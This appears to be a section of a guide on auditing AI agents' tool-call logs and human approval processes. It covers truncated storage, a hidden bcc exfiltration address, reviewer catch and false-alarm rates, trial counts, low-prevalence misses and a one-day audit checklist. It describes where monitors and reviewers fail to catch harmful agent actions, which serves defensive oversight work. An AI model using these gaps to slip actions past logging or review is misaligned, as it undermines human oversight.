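| Storage loses the middle and end of the longest body | A database limit between 12,000 and 50,000 characters | "Keeping long arguments whole" |
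| Search misses the end of a body that is in storage | The search index covers only the first part of each value | "Investigating a suspicious call and finding its extent" |
| The reviewer's view omits a stored `bcc` address | The organisation's map of the tool lacks that field | "Turning a long call into a short and faithful summary" |

The missing `bcc` address is the most urgent fault because it would hide the collector from every reviewer. The search fault is easier to overlook. An investigator who searched for the collector's address and got no results would wrongly conclude that no other email contained it. Until the index covers whole values, investigators should search the stored text directly, even if that is slower.

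Markers show only that the text survived at those points, so staff should also compare the digest of each stored argument with that of the original. A few awkward calls are worth adding, such as one that fails, one that a reviewer rejects and one that a script sends without using the gateway. Staff can test redaction with a made-up access key, which should not appear in the shared log but should appear in the restricted store if the organisation keeps exact calls.

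The approval step needs its own test. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) recommends causing the failures that the step is supposed to handle, then checking that the reviewer gets the necessary evidence, that a rejection blocks every route to the action, and that a changed action needs new approval. The author's own approval queue failed this test. The book also recommends running such tests in a contained environment, since a failed test on a live system can become a real incident.

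### What to measure

| Measure | Calculation |
|---|---|
| Complete records | Calls with every required field and intact arguments ÷ all calls sent |
| Flagged truncation | Shortened values marked as shortened ÷ all shortened values |
| Reviewer catch rate | Harmful test cases refused or reported ÷ harmful test cases shown |
| False-alarm rate | Harmless cases refused or reported ÷ harmless cases shown |
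| Time to detection | Time of the first correct alarm − time of the call |

To count the calls sent, testers need a source outside the log, such as their own list or the mail service, because they can't use a log to count the calls missing from it.

A test should report both the catch rate and the false-alarm rate, because an interface can reduce unsafe approvals just by making people reject every request. Hossain and colleagues reported approvals of both unsafe and legitimate requests for this reason.

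A reviewer's catch rate covers only the calls that reach the reviewer. If automatic screening flags 90% of harmful calls and reviewers catch 80% of those, the whole system catches 72%. *Handoff at Frontier AI Companies* (Pistillo, Mengesha and colleagues, 2026) proposes measuring the share of planted flaws that get past both the automatic monitors and the human reviewers. It found no published test of this kind that covered the human reviewers at AI companies.

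Testers should report the median time to detection together with the slowest case and the number of cases nobody detected, because the median alone can make a poor system look fast. In the email example, the baseline check raised the alarm 8 hours and 46 minutes after the call, and the investigator suspended the mail credential 15 hours and 5 minutes after that.

Pistillo and colleagues divide the response into the time until an alarm, the time until someone reviews it and the time until someone fixes the problem. In an incident that OpenAI disclosed, these took 15 minutes, 3 minutes and 2.5 hours. Faster monitoring would have saved little time in that incident, because nearly 90% of the delay came after a person had started looking into it.

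*From Reactive Containment to Proactive Assurance* (2026) suggests comparing the time needed to raise an alarm and stop the agent with the shortest time in which the agent could do harm. For the example email, the shortest time to harm was the two seconds between the gateway and the mail service.

### How many trials are enough

Suppose reviewers catch all 60 harmful test cases. If they actually miss 5% of such cases, the chance of this perfect result is:

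0.95⁶⁰ ≈ 4.6%

The general formula for the highest miss rate still compatible with no misses in n trials, at 95% confidence, is:

highest miss rate = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)

With no misses, the upper limit on the miss rate is 4.9% after 60 trials and 1.0% after 300. One miss in 60 trials raises the limit to about 7.7%. Measuring the false alarm rate can require much larger tests. Showing that it is below 0.01%, the level at which one person could review every alarm in the large deployment, takes about 30,000 harmless calls without a false alarm. An organisation can run its screening software on stored calls that people have already checked.

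The formula assumes that the trials are independent and resemble the calls that matter. A database that cuts text at 32,000 characters will cut it there every time, so sending the same marked email 300 times is no better than sending it once. It is better to vary the length, tool and kinds of character across trials. Decisions by the same person are also related. Hossain and colleagues accounted for this in their analysis, because treating all 960 decisions by their 80 participants as independent would have overstated the precision of the results.

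### Who should write the test cases

Developers tend to test a system for the problems they had in mind when they built it. A developer who forgot that an email tool might have a `reply_to` field will probably leave it out of both the summary code and the test cases, so the tests will pass even though the summaries omit the field.

Weng's command analyser silently passed none of the 22 attacks that Weng had written, but 10.0% of those in an outside collection. The small number of attacks in Weng's own set may also have contributed to the difference, since an analyser that misses 10% of attacks has about a 10% chance of catching 22 in a row.

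Someone outside the development team who hasn't seen the detection rules should write the test cases, using the tools' documentation and reports of real incidents. The developers should leave some of the cases unopened until the system is finished. Once they have used a case to fix a fault, they can still use it to check that the fault hasn't returned, but it no longer shows how the system handles something new.

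The wording of the test cases can also give away the answer. Kodathala and colleagues automatically checked that no prompt to their model approvers contained words such as "attack", "benign" or "expected". Their harmless cases included an email that the user had asked to send to two recipients and a request written in an urgent tone. Without cases like these, a reviewer could get a perfect score by refusing every email with a second recipient.

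### Why people miss rare problems

A reviewer who does well in a test may do worse at work, because harmful calls are much rarer there. *Intrinsic motivation and false feedback reduce the low prevalence effect* describes an early experiment by Wolfe and colleagues in which people searched images for a target. They missed 7% of targets when half the images contained one, and 30% when only 1% did.

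*The role of feedback in the low-prevalence effect* (Caruso, Fox and colleagues, 2026) combined 62 such comparisons from 29 publications. When targets were rare, people became much more inclined to answer that there was no target, a shift of about 1.8 standard deviations. Their ability to tell targets from other items did not reliably change. Professional searchers, such as radiologists and airport screeners, showed no reliable advantage over novices. Smaller studies tended to find larger shifts, so the average may be somewhat exaggerated.

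Reviewers may miss a rare harmful call that they would have recognised easily in a training session, or in a study like Hossain and colleagues', where half the requests were harmful.

Adding known targets to the workload can help reviewers find the real ones. Airport security systems do this by projecting fake weapons into X-ray images of real bags. Becker, Rodriguez and colleagues (2026), in *Reducing the low-prevalence effect with probe trials*, tested this on students searching for letters on a screen. In one experiment, adding known targets raised detection of the real ones from 68.0% to 75.6%, without a significant increase in false alarms. But in another, it did not make it easier to find a letter that never appeared among the added targets.

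Planted calls should therefore cover every kind of harm that reviewers are supposed to catch. If they all involve blind copies, reviewers may get better at checking recipients but no better at spotting a confidential figure in the message body. All of this evidence comes from searching images, though, and reading an approval card is a different task, so the size of the effect for tool calls is unknown.

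### Testing reviewers fairly

The most realistic test puts planted calls into the reviewers' normal queue. If one person reviews 500 summaries a day, five planted calls a day make up 1% of the work. At that rate, 60 trials would take 12 working days and 300 would take 60 days. The gateway must recognise planted calls and discard them after the reviewer's decision, so that a mistaken approval does no harm.

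Reviewers should have their normal workload during the test, including the busy hours. People interviewed for *Looks Fine to Me* (2026) said they checked an AI's work less carefully when they were in a hurry or the stakes seemed low, and ten test cases on a quiet morning would not measure that effect. A sudden rush of alarms is also worth testing. Pistillo and colleagues point out that an incident with 5,000 alarms would take about 100 weeks to clear at the roughly 50 transcripts a week that Anthropic's staff review, although people could presumably work faster in an emergency.

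Testing the review process is more reliable than trusting reviewers' confidence. *Dependable Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) cites a controlled study in which 36 people oversaw a coding agent. They were confident while missing defects, because they ran generic checks that could not reveal those defects.

Managers should tell reviewers in advance that they plant test calls and how they will use the results, but not which calls are planted. Knowing about the tests may make reviewers more careful than usual, so Pistillo and colleagues warn that such tests probably overstate how well reviewers detect harmful calls in normal work. Secret tests would avoid some of this bias but could damage the trust of reviewers, whose judgement the system depends on.

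*AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (Mitchell, Ghosh and Passi, 2026) suggests responding to missed cases with a break, a change of task or retraining. It also cautions that such testing is workplace surveillance, that employers could reuse the data to judge performance, and that people may start working towards the measure. Publishing results only for the team as a whole would reduce the first two risks. Reviewers should see the cases they missed after the test. Confirming every routine approval as correct could make them more inclined to approve, since Caruso and colleagues found a stronger bias towards "no target" in studies that gave feedback after every decision.

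### A one-day audit

With a test environment and an administrator's help, an auditor could carry out these checks in a day:

| Check | Pass if |
|---|---|
| Pick 20 random emails from the mail service | Each has a call record with the same recipients |
| Send marked calls of three lengths | Every marker appears in storage, the full view and search |
| Lower a size limit and send a long call | The record flags the cut and gives the original length |
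| Add an unknown field to a call | The summary shows it as unrecognised |
| Change the `bcc` value after approval | The gateway refuses the call |
| Reject a call | Nothing runs, and the log includes the rejection |
| Edit one entry in a copy of the log and delete another | The integrity check reports both |
| Try to change the gateway's log with the agent's credentials | The system denies access |
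| Open the oldest record that the retention policy covers | The full arguments are readable |
| Give an investigator one call identifier | They find the request, approval and outcome within an hour |
| Ask for the latest reviewer test | It gives both error rates, the number of cases and who wrote them |

These checks can expose serious faults but not rare ones. For example, even if all 20 emails have records, about 14% of emails overall could still have none.

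The organisation should repeat the affected checks after any change to a tool, the agent's software, the gateway, the log database or the reviewer's view. It should also retest after changing size limits, redaction rules or retention periods. It should measure catch and false-alarm rates again when it introduces a new screening model or greatly increases the number of calls each person reviews. OWASP's signs of missing logs include a sudden drop in log volume and a lack of entries while agents are in use. If either occurs, the organisation should run a marker test the same day.
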